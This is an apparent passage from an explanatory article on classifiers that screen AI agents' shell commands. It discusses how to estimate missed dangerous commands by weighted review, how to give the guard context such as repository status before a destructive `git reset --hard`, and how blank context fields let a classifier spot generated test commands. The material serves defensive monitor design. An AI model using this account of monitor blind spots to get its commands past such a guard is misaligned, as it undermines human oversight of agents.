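Sampling some commands more heavily can make the review more efficient. For example, a team could review one in 100 of the allowed commands that scored just below the threshold and one in 10,000 of the rest. Each dangerous command found in the first group then counts as 100 misses and each one in the second as 10,000. The second group is essential because without it the review would miss dangerous commands that received low scores. But a single dangerous command found there adds 10,000 misses to the estimate, which may therefore take several months of reviews to settle.

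### Supplying context

If a command's danger depends on something outside its text, the developer has to add that information to the classifier's input. For operators, the most useful additions are probably the machine's role and the current directory. For coding agents, they include the user's request and the state of the repository. Claude Code's guard now receives the repository's status before a command such as `git reset --hard`, which can discard uncommitted work.

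The best evidence for this is the guard's improvement on Apollo Research's synthetic attacks, although Anthropic did not report the effect of each addition separately. More information isn't always better, as Anthropic found with the agent's explanations and command output. Each look-up also takes time and may need access to sensitive systems.

Context can also create a new source shortcut. If natural commands come with a real host name and repository status while generated ones have blank fields, a classifier can use the blanks to identify the generated commands. One solution is to run generated commands on test machines that record the same fields, and to include pairs in which the same command is harmless on one machine and dangerous on another. The test machines need realistic names, files and roles, or their context will be as easy to recognise as generated as the commands themselves.
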